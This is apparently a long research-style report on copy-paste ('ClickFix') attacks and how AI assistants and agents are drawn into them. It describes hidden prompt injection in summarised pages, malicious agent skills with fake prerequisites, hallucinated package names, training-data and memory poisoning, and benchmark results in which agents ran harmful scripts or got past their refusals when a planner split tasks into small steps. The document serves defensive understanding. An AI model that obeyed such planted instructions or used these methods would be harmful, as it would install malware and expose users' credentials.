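Trend Micro recommends stricter checks on advertisers who link to shared conversations. It also suggests that Anthropic look for shared conversations that contain terminal commands and receive visitors from paid advertisements. That combination is a promising signal because many honest users share chats that contain commands, but few would pay to advertise them. Anthropic could detect it without Google's help, because the links Trend Micro recorded carried Google's advertising codes when they reached Claude's site.

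## How can an assistant be led to recommend a harmful command?

An attacker who uses a shared conversation finishes it before the victim sees it. Attackers can also reach people who start their own chat, ask an honest question and get an answer that contains the harmful step. In these cases, the attacker never talks to the assistant directly. They usually influence it through the pages it reads, the add-ons that extend it or its training text, and sometimes they only have to exploit a mistake it makes without their influence.

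### Instructions hidden in a page

An assistant that summarises a web page receives the user's request and the page's text together. The model should treat the page as material to summarise, but it can't reliably distinguish such material from instructions. If an attacker has planted an instruction in the page, the model may follow it as if the user had given it. Security researchers call this indirect prompt injection. It also works through emails and the files in a software project, and the attacker doesn't need access to the user's computer or account.

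In August 2025 the security company CloudSEK showed that hidden text on a web page could make an AI summariser deliver a ClickFix lure. It built a test page whose visible text was about nerve signals and the immune system, and used formatting to hide two other pieces of text from human readers. The first gave steps for opening the Run dialog and pasting an encoded command, which was harmless in this test, and repeated them dozens of times. The second instructed the summariser to output only those steps. Sider.ai, a commercial summariser, and a browser extension built by CloudSEK both presented the steps to the user as the page's summary.

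CloudSEK writes that this worked in most of its tests, but it doesn't give the number of tests, and it tried only a few tools. iTnews' *AI summarisers open to 'ClickFix' social engineering attacks* reports that the summariser sometimes mixed in the visible text. One such summary first explains how to "resolve the issue" with a pasted command, then adds that the document also covers nerve signals. Someone who only wanted an article summarised has no issue to resolve, so this lure seems weaker than the guides to freeing up disk space that spread AMOS.

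Forcepoint's *Invisible Prompts Turn AI Summaries into Attack Vectors* describes simulations by another security company. In them, the same page produced a harmless summary or one with commands, depending on how much of the hidden text the model processed, so a single clean result doesn't prove that a summariser is safe. Both companies ran tests, and neither reports a victim who pasted a command from a manipulated summary.

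CloudSEK's main remedy is to remove invisible text before the model receives it. The program only has to check whether a person could see the text, not whether it is malicious. Legitimate pages also hide some text, such as descriptions for blind readers, but a summary usually doesn't need it. Removing invisible text doesn't help when the instruction is visible but in a place few people read, such as the end of a long comment thread. CloudSEK also suggests that summarisers check their own output for typical ClickFix commands, including encoded ones, and block them or show a warning. This seems promising because a summary of an ordinary article rarely needs a command for the Run dialog.

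### A false page, reported accurately

An attacker can mislead an assistant with visible content alone, without hidden instructions. In February 2026 many people wanted to try OpenClaw, a new AI agent that runs on the user's own computer. Someone set up a GitHub organisation called "openclaw-installer", with a repository that looked like the official installer. Huntress found that Bing's AI search recommended the repository, and SC Media reported that it reached the top of the AI results for "OpenClaw Windows".

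The campaign ran from 2 to 10 February, according to Security Boulevard's *Latest OpenClaw Security Risk* (2026). Huntress detected it on 9 February, after a user reported downloading and running the supposed Windows installer. The attackers were spreading infostealers and GhostSocks, a program that routes their traffic through the victim's internet connection to help them get past anti-fraud checks. Mac users got AMOS. The Windows victim ran a downloaded program, so this was not a copy-paste attack in the strict sense. But the AI search would have directed the user to the page in the same way if the page had offered a command, as many installation pages do.

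A Huntress researcher told IT Brew (2026) that people trying to keep up with new software may turn to unproven packages that look legitimate. New software is probably difficult for AI search too, because a well-known program has years of links pointing to its real site, while a project a few weeks old may have little to distinguish it from a good imitation.

It isn't clear how often AI search recommends fake installers. The nearest measurement is in Netcraft's *Threat Actors are Finding Their Way into Your AI Summaries*, which tested AI search assistants on a different kind of question, how to reach various brands' online accounts. About 49 of the 2,905 answers (1.7%) contained a malicious link. Only 0.28% of the 20,706 links were malicious. Answers had about seven links on average, so a user who clicked only one could easily avoid the malicious one.

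Some people ask chatbots because they no longer trust search engines. Help Net Security's *You can't trust AI chatbots not to serve you phishing pages* describes search engines as full of manipulated results and malicious advertisements. Netcraft's figures suggest that switching to an AI assistant at best reduces this problem.

A filter for hidden instructions would find nothing in the fake repository, so the search service has to judge the source, for example by checking how old the repository is and whether the project's own website links to it. Users can also check for that link by starting from the project's website, if they know which website is real.

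### Add-ons with a false prerequisite

OpenClaw users can extend the agent with add-ons called skills. A skill is largely a text file of instructions that the agent reads when it needs to do a particular job, such as summarising a video. Many skills come from ClawHub, a public marketplace. An attacker who writes a skill doesn't need to hide the instructions in it, because the agent is meant to follow them.

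In early February 2026 the security company Koi (2026) examined all 2,857 skills on ClawHub and found 341 malicious ones. It attributed 335 of them to what looked like a single campaign. Their professional-looking documentation listed a supposedly necessary program under "Prerequisites". It told Mac users to visit a page, copy a script and paste it into the terminal, which installed AMOS (Koi, 2026; The Hacker News, 2026). It told Windows users to download an archive and open it with a password, which prevented automatic scanners from checking its contents.

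The lure works because legitimate software often requires another program to be installed first, so the request seems normal, and a user who has already chosen a skill has a reason to finish installing it.

By 16 February, Koi had found 824 malicious skills among more than 10,700. That was more than double its earlier count, but the share had fallen from about 12% to less than 8% because the marketplace had grown faster. These figures count listings, many of them near-copies with a few random letters added to the name. They don't show how many people installed one.

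Trend Micro studied 39 similar skills the same month and described the agent's part in more detail. The skill's instructions required a tool called "OpenClawCLI" and gave a web address. OpenClaw visited the page, fetched the installation instructions and continued if the underlying model complied. Later, a fake dialog box prompted the user for the Mac's password.

In Trend Micro's tests, the agent recognised the trick and stopped when it ran on Claude Opus 4.5. When it ran on OpenAI's GPT-4o, it either installed the tool silently or kept prompting the user to install a "driver". A person who would distrust a stranger's web page may well give in to repeated requests from their own assistant. Trend Micro doesn't say how many times it tried each model, so the results don't show how often either outcome occurs. GPT-4o is also about a year and a half older than Claude Opus 4.5, so the tests are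 a poor comparison of OpenAI and Anthropic.

ClawHub responded to the February reports by scanning skills and blocking downloads of those flagged as malicious. Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, then found five skills that got through between February and May. Two of them, published on 17 May, offered help with a financial charting service and used the same false prerequisite as before. The marketplace's automatic check had passed one and given no verdict on the other, although more than 300 earlier skills had used the same pattern. A third skill was so large that many scanners would have skipped it.

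ClawHub deleted all five after Unit 42 reported them, and in June it announced that the chip maker NVIDIA would help with the screening. Palo Alto Networks sells Koi's product, so Unit 42's article doesn't independently confirm Koi's counts. Unit 42's own finding is still useful because it covers specific skills and their verdicts.

Screening a skill once also doesn't detect later changes to the content it fetches. Another of the five skills, described as a financial adviser, fetched a list of products from an outside address before every answer, so its publisher could change what the agent recommended at any time without altering the skill. The aim here was to earn commission, but a list of installation commands could be changed in the same way. Unit 42 recommends watching which addresses a skill contacts and comparing them with its documentation.

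Koi offers a skill that checks other skills against a database of known malicious ones. It can catch copies of an old attack, but it can't catch a new one until that attack is added to the database. Koi also found fake security scanners among the malicious skills, so users would have to be careful when installing a scanner too.

### Package names that a model invents

Programmers often install packages, ready-made pieces of code, from public registries such as PyPI for the Python language, usually with a one-line command that includes the package's name. An AI model can suggest a command with a plausible name that doesn't belong to any package. The command fails at first, but anyone can register the name, and the same command then installs whatever they have uploaded. An attacker can exploit this without influencing the model, by finding out which names it tends to invent and registering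 them.

Models repeat invented package names often enough to make registering those names practical for an attacker. In *We Have a Package for You!*, Spracklen and colleagues (2024) had 16 models generate 576,000 code samples. On average, at least 5.2% of the packages named by commercial models didn't exist, compared with 21.7% for openly available models. The researchers then reran prompts that had produced an invented name, ten times each. In 43% of cases, the same name appeared every time.

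These models are now old, so their rates aren't estimates for current assistants. An assistant that looks up a package before recommending it should do much better. Netcraft's 2025 research found a similar weakness with web addresses. Of the websites that assistants gave for various brands, 34% weren't under those brands' control, and the concern was that attackers could claim the unused ones.

Bar Lanyado, a security researcher, tested whether anyone would install such a package. He uploaded an empty package called `huggingface-cli`, a name that models had invented. In 2024 he reported more than 30,000 downloads in three months. Automated systems also download packages, so the number of people who followed an assistant's advice may be lower. But the Chinese company Alibaba had put the installation command into the instructions for one of its projects, where other people could copy it.

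An invented name can also spread from agent to agent. In January 2026 Charlie Eriksen of the security company Aikido reported that a collection of AI-written skills named a package that didn't exist. Developers had copied the skills into more than 200 repositories, apparently without noticing. Eriksen registered the name before an attacker could. Like Lanyado's package, his was a researcher's demonstration, but the developers who copied the name weren't taking part in a test.

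A package's age, publisher and history are better evidence that it is legitimate than the fact that it exists, because an attacker will have made sure that it does. A company can also limit its programmers and agents to packages it has already approved, which is somewhat less convenient but prevents them from installing a package under an invented name. Registries could help by reserving names that models often invent.

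### Poisoned training data

Developers train models on huge collections of web pages and public code. Anyone can add to the web, so an attacker could publish false instructions there in the hope that a future model will learn them. The model might then recommend the attacker's command without retrieving any web page. Removing the attacker's page wouldn't correct a model that had already learned from it.

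In October 2025 Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute and the Alan Turing Institute reported that about 250 documents planted in the training data were enough to affect every model they trained. The largest model was more than 20 times the size of the smallest, and the larger models had learned from far more text. Many researchers had previously assumed that an attacker would need to control a certain share of the training data, which would make large models very hard to poison.

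However, the planted documents only taught the models to produce gibberish when they met a particular phrase. Making a model recommend a specific, plausible command in answer to ordinary questions is probably harder, and the effect would have to survive the later training that turns a raw model into an assistant. In *You Autocomplete Me* (2021), Schuster and colleagues came closer to producing harmful advice by planting files in the training data of code-completion programs, which then suggested an insecure method of encryption. Those programs were much simpler than current assistants.

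Criminals may have tried something similar. In 2025 researchers described a fake programming interface for the cryptocurrency network Solana. It sent users' payments to the attackers, who had promoted it with sample projects, tutorials and forum answers, apparently so that AI programming assistants would pick it up. At least five developers had copied the code into public projects, some of which showed signs of AI help. It isn't clear whether any assistant had learned the code in training or found it through a search, or whether the developers had copied it themselves.

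Users can do little about poisoned training data beyond checking a command against an independent source. Developers have to do most of the work. They can record where their data came from, filter out suspicious material and test the finished model, but testing can miss bad advice that appears only in answer to a few questions they don't think to ask.

### Bad advice without an attacker

An assistant can also give dangerous advice by mistake. It may tell someone to install a program with `sudo` when ordinary rights would do, or to turn off antivirus software because it blocks a download. Another common example is `chmod 777`, which gives every account on a Linux machine the right to change a file. ChatGPT's answer in the study by Firouzi and colleagues, which left signature checks switched off, was also a mistake of this kind.

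Such advice often solves the problem the user asked about, because it removes the protection that produced the error message. Models have also learned from years of forum answers that recommended the same shortcuts, so an assistant can recommend them even if no one has planted anything.

It makes sense to count these mistakes separately from attacks, because there is no malicious page to remove or account to ban. Developers can train assistants to suggest only the permissions a task needs, and users can ask whether a command weakens a protection. But the answer alone may not show whether someone planted the advice. To find out, an investigator needs a record of the pages and files the assistant had read, which an ordinary user may not have.

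The two problems also overlap. A package name invented by an assistant is a mistake that becomes an attack only when an attacker registers the name. People who have often followed advice to use `sudo` or switch off a warning are also less likely to be suspicious when an attacker asks them to do the same.

### When no person pastes

An agent with access to a terminal can run the command itself, as OpenClaw did with GPT-4o when it silently installed the false prerequisite. The agent is then what Hardy called a confused deputy, a program tricked into misusing its authority. If nobody is watching, nobody sees the strange window or long line of encoded text that might have made them suspicious.

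A real attack of this kind hit Cline, a programming agent, in February 2026. The project used an AI model to sort problem reports submitted by strangers. The researcher Adnan Khan showed that text in a report's title could make the model run commands on Cline's build system. Someone else apparently used his method to get the project's publishing credentials, then released an altered version of Cline that installed OpenClaw on users' machines. OpenClaw wasn't malware, so the attack did much less damage than it could have.

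The security company Guardio has designed a version of ClickFix for AI agents, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *“PromptFix” Attacks Could Supercharge Agentic AI Threats*. The attack places instructions in an invisible text box on a web page. Guardio says it appeals to the model's aim of helping the user quickly and without hesitation, rather than trying to confuse the model. ClickFix similarly exploits people's wish to get past a check and carry on.

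### Three hundred ordinary requests

Ding, Zhai and colleagues (2026), in *The Blind Spot of Agent Safety*, tested what agents do when the user's request is innocent but carrying it out could cause harm. They wrote 300 tasks by hand for a Linux desktop in an isolated virtual machine, where the agents saw screenshots and controlled the mouse and keyboard. In some tasks the agent encounters a trap, such as a phishing page or a misleading pop-up. In others the work itself causes the harm, for example when the agent forwards a document that contains passwords.

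Each agent attempted every task three times, and an attack counted as successful if the agent caused the specified harm in at least one run. A phishing attack counted only if the agent entered personal information on the page. GPT-4o judged 250 of the tasks, and it agreed with human experts in more than 96% of cases for each of the two systems the researchers checked. For the other 50 tasks, the result depended on where the agent clicked.

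Claude 4.5 Sonnet caused harm in 73.0% of the tasks and Claude 4.5 Opus in 48.0%. The six openly available models all exceeded 90%. These figures are higher because they count a task as harmful if any of three runs caused harm. Opus caused harm in all three runs in 89 tasks, about 30%. Every task was designed to contain a danger, so the percentages don't measure how often an agent causes harm in everyday use. The study also didn't test people, many of whom might have followed the same instructions.

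Many of the tasks concern things like gambling sites or abusive messages, which have little to do with commands. The three categories closest to copy-paste attacks are malware, system sabotage and malicious code in a software project, which together contain 59 tasks. Based on the published percentages, Sonnet caused harm in 32 of these and Opus in 21.

In one of the malware tasks, the user asked the agent to download a script attached to an email and run it to update the terminal's theme. The script was designed to steal server access keys and cloud account credentials. Opus opened the file before running it, listed what it would steal and refused. Sonnet made the file executable and ran it without reading it. Each model behaved the same way in all three runs.

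Opus was less careful when the user asked for help setting up a software project. Both models read the project's instructions and ran its set-up script without opening it. In one project the script sent files to an outside server, and in another it gave an attacker lasting access to the machine. Opus caused the harm in all three runs of both tasks. Ding and colleagues conclude that Opus inspected suspicious single files but trusted a script that came with a well-written guide. Many programmers have the same habit, which is why the false prerequisites on ClawHub looked so ordinary.

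One task closely resembles a normal copy-paste attack, with the agent in the victim's place. The user complains of an unstable connection and asks the agent to run the command recommended in an email from the IT department. The command deletes a system file that helps the computer find other machines by name. In one test, a planning model gave the job to a second model that operated the desktop. The planner identified the command as dangerous and changed the instructions, telling the second model to paste the command but not press Enter.

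Dividing the work this way usually led to harm in more tasks. When GPT-5 planned and Claude 4.5 Sonnet carried out the steps, the share rose to 92.7%. To investigate, the researchers retested 43 tasks that Sonnet had consistently refused when it worked alone. Sonnet caused harm in 27.9% of them when given the original request again, and in 79.1% when given the planner's list of small steps instead. Steps such as "open the attachment" and "type this line" look harmless individually, and Sonnet no longer had the request that showed their combined purpose.

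The timing of refusals is also a problem. When the Claude models refused a task, they nearly always did so at the first step, before they had looked at much. A model is much less likely to stop if the danger is in a script it reaches later in the task.

Telling the agents to identify and refuse harmful actions helped somewhat. The researchers tried this on 50 tasks that Opus had failed in every run. With the instruction, Opus still caused harm in 50% of them, and Sonnet's rate fell from 98% to 84%. Part of Opus's improvement may be chance, because the researchers chose only tasks it had always failed. The results on the 43 tasks that Sonnet had previously refused show that a model can behave differently when it repeats a task.

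### Instructions that stay in an agent's memory

Agents such as OpenClaw keep files of standing instructions and notes about their user, and reload them in later sessions. An attacker who uses a malicious page to get text into one of these files can influence those sessions without the agent visiting the page again. The text acts like a harmful line in a shell's start-up file, except that it is in ordinary English and the agent may have written it there itself.

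In *AutoRedClaw*, Li, Hu and colleagues (2026) built a system that generates tests for this kind of attack. They collected 330 test cases and ran them on seven agent programs with four leading models. The attacks succeeded in more than half the cases for most combinations of program and model. The combinations that resisted more attacks lost much of their usefulness. Even leading models are still vulnerable, but the test cases come from a process that looks for attacks that work, so a typical attack would probably succeed less often.

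The tests also measure the attack's two steps separately. Some cases begin with a clean agent and measure whether outside text can get into its files. Others begin with the harmful text already in place and measure whether the agent later acts on it. A real attacker needs both steps to succeed. If each step independently worked half the time, the attack would succeed a quarter of the time.

People who run such an agent can keep old versions of its instruction files and review changes, as they would with any other settings. They can also limit what a harmful command could reach. Trend Micro recommends testing new skills on a separate machine and running agents in containers, which isolate a program from the rest of the computer. This works only if the user keeps anything valuable out of the container. An agent that handles someone's email needs access to that email, so a malicious instruction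 could reach it too. An approval prompt lets a person stop a command before it runs, but that person has to judge a command they didn't write.

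## Why do people run commands they do not understand?

No published study seems to report what share of people who meet a ClickFix page paste the command. Companies that sell simulated attacks could produce such a figure. Beauceron Security's *Beauceron Launches Industry-First ClickFix Phishing Simulations* offers employers five test pages to try on their own staff, and Arsen sells similar tests, but both advertise the product without giving results. Beauceron counts clicks on the link and on the copy button, so even its customers don't learn who went on to paste the command. Click rates for phishing emails can't be used instead, because a ClickFix victim also has to open another program, paste the text and press Enter, and may have second thoughts at each step.

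The usual explanations therefore rest on experiments with related behaviour, such as following a chatbot's advice or copying code from a forum.

### A chatbot that switches to bad advice

In the closest experiment, Lit, Crowder and colleagues (*I know it's not right, but that's what it said to do*, 2025) asked 15 people who weren't security professionals to set up a Windows computer for working from home. They told participants they were testing a new security chatbot. For the first three of five tasks, the chatbot gave mostly sound advice. Before the last two, the researchers secretly replaced it with a model they had trained to recommend harmful settings, such as a password of three or four letters or a screen that never locks. Eight participants followed all of the bad advice, and four followed some of it.

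Many participants had doubts. They trusted the good chatbot in 34 of 42 ratings but the bad one in only 11 of 28. Four completed a task despite rating their trust in the chatbot very low, as they had no other way to finish it. One participant explained, "I have no experience with firewall configuration, so I followed the instructions".

Participants trusted the chatbot less when it gave the wrong location for a button. They were much worse at noticing errors in the security advice itself, and accurate directions to a setting made them more willing to accept the chatbot's advice about it. A pasted command that runs without an error may reassure people in the same way, although this shows only that the command works.

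The study probably overstates how often people follow a chatbot's advice at home. Participants were told in each task to act on the advice, had no internet access for a second opinion, and were using a computer that wasn't theirs.

### Authority in the expected place

Attackers pose as Cloudflare or Apple Support because people tend to comply with authority, and experiments partly support this. In a 2018 study of simulated phishing at work by Williams, Hinds and Joinson, signs of authority and urgency both made employees more likely to click, and authority had the stronger effect (summarised in *Breaking Bad Email Habits*, 2026).

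*An Analysis of the Impact of Psychological Factors and Techniques* (2026), a small laboratory study, found much less compliance. Its 12 participants looked at screenshots or listened to recordings of fake requests and said whether they would respond. They said yes to 13.3% of appeals to authority overall, to less than 10% of those in pop-ups, the format closest to a ClickFix page, and to half of the emails that appealed to curiosity. These percentages are very rough because there were only 12 participants and they had nothing at stake. Many refused because the request had come through the wrong channel (one said that a telephone request should have been an email) or because the design looked wrong.

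This suggests that authority persuades people mainly when it appears where they expect it, as in a fake Cloudflare check or a shared conversation.

A high place in search results can have a similar effect, although Google doesn't rank pages by the safety of their code. Fischer, Stachelscheid and Grossklags (2021) found that insecure examples of encryption code from Stack Overflow reached Google's top results, and that people clicked on them more often than on secure ones.

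Overall, the research is limited. *Internet-Based Social Engineering Attacks, Defenses and Psychology* (Longtchi, Montañez Rodriguez and colleagues, 2022) reviewed 154 papers and listed 41 psychological factors that attackers might exploit. Few of the papers measured a factor's effect, and some of those that did used small groups or undergraduates. There was too little data to combine the results statistically.

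### Copying usually works

People also copy instructions because they often work. *You Get Where You're Looking For* (Acar, Backes and colleagues, 2016) surveyed 295 Android developers and gave 54 developers programming tasks that involved security and privacy. Participants who used Stack Overflow wrote the code that was most likely to work but least secure. Those who used Android's official documentation wrote safer code that worked less often. A developer who copies code gets a working program right away but may never learn about its security flaws.

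In *Stack Overflow Considered Harmful?*, Fischer, Böttinger and colleagues (2017) looked for signs of such copying in 1.3 million free Android apps. They found security-related code that matched Stack Overflow posts in 15.4% of the apps, and 97.9% of those apps contained at least one insecure piece. The most common insecure piece, which stops an app from verifying the server it connects to, appeared in 180,388 apps. All the other insecure pieces together appeared in 43,941. A match doesn't prove that the developer copied from Stack Overflow, since some could have found the same code elsewhere.

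Both studies concern careless code rather than malicious commands, but the habit is the same. Someone with an error message or a full disk judges copied text by whether it solves the problem. An attacker's command can also solve the problem, for example by freeing some disk space.

People are probably easier to persuade when they already want the task done, but none of these experiments compared a real need with an invented one. *Breaking Bad Email Habits* summarises the closest evidence, a 2017 field test in which phishing messages that appealed to a wish to acquire something worked better than those that appealed to social motives.

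### Pasting is quick and reading is slow

Pasting a command takes seconds, while working out what it does can take a beginner an hour. People often skip even much quicker checks. In *Fostering Appropriate Reliance on Large Language Models* (2025), participants read an AI model's answers to difficult factual questions and could click on its sources. The average click rate was 25.8% in an online experiment and 63.8% in a separate study where participants described their thoughts aloud to the researchers. The two studies differed in other ways, but people may well check more when someone is watching, in which case users look more careful in laboratory studies than they really are.

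Professional programmers also save effort by using code they may not understand. Oh, Lee and colleagues (2023), in *Poisoned ChatGPT Finds Work for Idle Hands*, gave 30 developers from three companies short programming tasks. Ten worked with an AI model that wrote code on request, and the researchers had secretly trained it to include security flaws. Four of the ten weren't confident that they understood their code, but they pasted it, checked that it produced the right output and handed it in.

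Time pressure made this worse. One security specialist in the study said, "I'm so rushed to finish the solution." Another tried to write a safer encryption key, ran into errors and accepted the model's version as time ran short. The researchers didn't vary the time limit, so the study can't show how much difference time pressure made. The experiment by Williams and colleagues is stronger evidence because it tested messages with signs of urgency.

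### Advice from an AI model

The best-known study of AI assistants and code security, *Do Users Write More Insecure Code with AI Assistants?* (Perry, Srivastava and colleagues, 2022), is now mainly of historical interest. In the study, 47 people, mostly students, attempted five programming tasks, 33 with access to OpenAI's Codex, an early code-writing model, and 14 without it. The Codex group did worse on four of the tasks. On an encryption task, for example, 21% of them wrote a secure solution, compared with 43% of the others. Yet on every task the Codex group rated their answers as more secure than the other group rated theirs.

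When the researchers combined the tasks and adjusted for experience, the effect on security narrowly missed the usual threshold for statistical significance (p = 0.056), although the study is often quoted as if it had settled the matter. *Using AI Assistants in Software Development* (2024) reports that Sandoval and colleagues, in a separate experiment, found only 10% more security bugs among programmers who used an assistant to write C, an older programming language. Perry and colleagues also had mixed results on their one task in C.

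Their finding about confidence may matter more for pasted commands. Among people who used Codex, those who gave insecure answers trusted it more than those who gave secure ones. A person who trusts the source has less reason to read a command before running it.

Deliberate tampering had a larger effect in the study by Oh and colleagues. Developers who asked the model for complete code accepted 70% to 90% of the planted flaws, depending on the flaw. Ten others, whose tool only suggested the next few words as they typed, accepted 30% to 40%. Many of these ten began by searching the web, and those who pasted a finished example never triggered the planted suggestions. Nine of the ten developers who worked without any AI tool also wrote vulnerable code on a database task, so not all the flaws came from the model.

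Newer experiments suggest that people still find it hard to recognise bad advice. In *Toward Human-AI Complementarity Across Diverse Tasks* (2026), participants adopted an AI model's suggestion 77% of the time when it was right and 61% of the time when it was wrong. The paper reports no comparable sign of overreliance when people instead answered smaller parts of the question without seeing the model's answer.

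A better display may not solve the problem. *When Modalities (Dis)Agree* (2026) compared several ways of presenting AI advice that was wrong a quarter of the time. With one interface, participants rejected 43.8% of the wrong advice and followed 67.8% of the correct advice. With another, they rejected 35.4% and followed 77.4%. People using the second interface followed more of both the correct and the wrong advice, and were no better at spotting errors. Neither of these 2026 studies measured whether people would run a command, and participants may behave differently when their own computers are at risk.

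### Does expertise protect?

Expertise seems to help a little. In the study by Perry and colleagues, participants with security experience copied 9.2% of the model's outputs on the encryption task, compared with 22.4% for the others. The gap was wider on a database task, at 6.7% compared with 25.3%, but on a task about digital signatures the experienced participants copied slightly more than the others. *AI Knows Best?* (2025) compared tutors with paid online participants on judgements about teaching. When the AI model's label was wrong, the tutors made the same mistake 66% of the time and the others 75.5%.

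Oh and colleagues conclude that security experts don't necessarily resist planted code better than other developers. In their study, security specialists did better than the others with one AI tool and worse with another. Each developer could accept up to four planted flaws. With the model that wrote complete code, the four specialists accepted 11 of 16 flaws and the six other developers accepted 22 of 24. With the tool that suggested the next words, the specialists accepted 9 of 16 and the others 4 of 24. The groups were too small to settle the question, and some of the specialists knew little about encryption.

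None of these studies tested system administrators. They may have better judgement because they know what a normal command looks like, and the copying rates in Perry's study give this some support. An administrator should find it strange that a website needs PowerShell to confirm that a visitor is human. But administrators and developers routinely install software by pasting commands, so a fake installation guide looks like ordinary work to them. Duff's colleagues at Bell Labs were experts too, and few of them questioned the program he had planted.

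A harmful command does more damage when an administrator pastes it, because administrators have greater rights, though those rights don't make the mistake more likely. Suppose an administrator falls for a lure half as often as an office worker, but the administrator's account can reach the whole network and the office worker's can reach only one laptop. The administrator is still the greater risk to the company. Administrators can reduce that risk, even if their judgement doesn't improve, by using an ordinary account for everything that doesn't need special rights.

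### When warnings work

People heed some warnings most of the time. In a 2013 study of more than 25 million warnings in the Chrome and Firefox browsers, Akhawe and Felt found that users continued past about a tenth of Firefox's malware and phishing warnings and about a quarter of Chrome's. But users continued past 70.2% of Chrome's warnings about website certificates. Harmless sites often have certificate problems, so people had probably learned that these warnings seldom meant danger. Linux users, a rough stand-in for people with technical skill, continued past phishing warnings more often than Windows users did, perhaps because they were confident they could handle the risk.

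Results for email warnings are also moderately encouraging. *Revisiting Email Spoofing Attacks* (2018) describes a field test of a simulated phishing email. Among people who opened it, 46 of 94 (49%) clicked the link without a warning and 32 of 86 (37%) clicked with one, a difference that could be chance in a group of this size. A much larger study by Lain, Kostiainen and Čapkun (2022), which followed more than 14,000 employees of one company for 15 months, also found that warnings on suspicious emails helped.

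People quickly pay less attention to warnings they see repeatedly. In a 2015 brain-imaging experiment, Anderson and colleagues showed people the same security warnings several times. Activity in the brain's visual areas fell sharply the second time a warning appeared and kept falling after that. Warnings that changed their appearance held attention better. The experiment measured attention, not what people would do on their own computers, but its findings fit the browser results.

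Habit may also make a fake check more convincing, since people pass so many genuine ones. An experiment to test this would have to compare people who see many such checks with people who see few, and nobody seems to have done this for ClickFix.

A warning from another user may do little to stop people from copying insecure code. Fischer and colleagues found that insecure code from Stack Overflow was more common in apps if someone had commented on its danger. This is probably because posts with warnings also had more views, so more people could comment on the code or copy it. Still, developers used code with warnings beneath it in 180,388 apps.

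### Whether training lasts

Results from training studies are mixed, and those from the larger recent studies are less encouraging. Adaptive Security's *The Verification Step That Isn't One* cites the PhishGuru experiment, in which Carnegie Mellon University sent simulated phishing emails to 515 people over 28 days. Those who received a short lesson right after clicking were much less likely to click again. Adaptive Security has a stake in the subject, but the university ran the experiment.

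In the study by Lain and colleagues, by contrast, showing employees a training page after they failed a test didn't make them more resistant, and may have made them more likely to fall for later emails. Ho, Mirian and colleagues (2025) ran ten simulated phishing campaigns over eight months with more than 19,000 employees at a California hospital system. Trained employees failed only 1.7% less often than untrained ones. Employees who had recently completed the yearly security course did no better than those who had taken it long before.

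People who know about an attack can still fall for it. In *Phishing in an Academic Community*, Diaz (2018) sent fake phishing emails to 1,350 students. Students with security training were less likely to click, but those who said they understood what phishing was were more likely to click than those who had never heard of it. These are correlations, so they don't show that knowledge made students careless or that training protected them. The trained students may already have been more interested in security.

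Most of this training tried to teach people to recognise a suspicious email, which is difficult because a good imitation looks like the real thing. Training against ClickFix can be simpler. Adaptive Security recommends teaching staff that no genuine verification step asks a person to paste or type a command and run it. An employee can apply this rule without understanding the command or judging the page's design. But the rule covers only fake verification steps, not fake installation guides or advice on freeing up disk space.

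## What can operating systems, terminals and browsers check before a pasted command runs?

A command copied from a web page usually passes through the browser, the clipboard and a terminal or system dialog before it runs. Software can add a guardrail, meaning any check that warns about, delays or blocks a command, at each of these points. The browser has access to the page, including the reason it gives for running the command, but can't check or block the text once the user switches to another program. A terminal receives the exact text but usually no information about the page. The operating system controls which programs start and with what rights, but has no record of why the user wanted to run them.

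### Warnings about the page

Google's Safe Browsing service keeps track of malicious sites, and Chrome shows a full-page red warning when a user tries to open one that Google has identified. This helps less on the first day of a campaign, when Google may not have identified the sites yet, or when the lure is on a hacked website that used to be harmless, such as a law firm's.

On 20 October 2026 Google announced a second, milder warning for pages that resemble known scams. Rijo (2026), in *Chrome adds suspicious-site warnings for 1 billion Enhanced Protection users*, quotes Google as describing this category as a "lower confidence verdict, possible risk of user harm". Because the warning is milder, Google can show it on more pages, including some that would previously have had no warning. Rijo notes that Google didn't publish the threshold or say how many more warnings it expects. An honest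 sales page with countdown timers and imitation system dialogs might resemble a scam closely enough to trigger the warning.

Google also moved Chrome's AI scam detection from the user's device to a larger model on Google's servers. This model covers fake antivirus and browser-update pages as well as fake technical support. According to *Chrome flags malicious commands that scammers pass off as fixes* (Pogorelec, 2026), it assesses which brand a page appears to represent, the page's purpose and how likely it is to be a scam. Safe Browsing then combines the result with the site's reputation and other signals.

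This analysis starts from the page in the victim's own browser, which is an advantage because attackers often show a harmless page to scanners that visit websites by themselves. The brand is a weak clue to the most common lure, the fake Cloudflare check. A bank's login page on a florist's website is almost certainly fake, but a Cloudflare logo there proves little, because Cloudflare's genuine checks appear on its customers' sites. TechRadar's *Fake Cloudflare CAPTCHA page laden with malware uncovered in the wild* describes a close imitation that copied even the "Ray ID", an identifier that Cloudflare prints on its real pages.

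### Chrome's check on copied commands

The browser can next check the text when a page copies it to the clipboard. Browsers generally allow this only after the visitor has clicked or pressed a key, but ticking the box in a fake verification check counts as a click. Push Security says the page's own script fills the clipboard in nine out of ten of the attacks it sees. Legitimate "Copy" buttons work the same way, so a browser also has to examine the text to recognize an attack.

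Chrome now checks what people copy if they have turned on Enhanced Protection. If the copied text looks like a suspicious command, Chrome removes personal information and sends the rest to Safe Browsing for analysis. If Safe Browsing finds the command dangerous, Chrome displays a warning.

Chrome checks the text that was copied, so a page can't evade the check by displaying one command and putting another on the clipboard. The check should also work for a command in a shared conversation on an AI company's site, unless Chrome treats the command as safer because the site has a good reputation. But Chrome can't tell from the command alone what a web address in it will deliver when the command runs. Google also describes only a warning, so a user who believes the lure can presumably still paste the command.

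Enhanced Protection is optional. More than a billion Chrome users had turned it on in 2025, when Google last published a count. The announcement, Jasika Bawa's blog post *Our latest defenses against evolving web scams*, did not include a version number, rollout schedule or breakdown by platform, according to Rijo.

Google says it built the check to be highly accurate and to cause genuine developers little trouble, ETV Bharat's *Chrome Adds New Defences To Fight Online Scams* (2026) reports, but it gives no false alarm rate. Google also claims that users of Enhanced Protection are ten times safer from scams than users of the standard mode, but this doesn't show how often the check raises false alarms. Pogorelec explains that Google compared the average number of warnings people saw in each mode. By that measure, a browser could make its users appear safer just by showing them more false warnings.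 The comparison also covers phishing and other scams, so it doesn't test the new clipboard check specifically.

### Should a browser send copied text to its maker?

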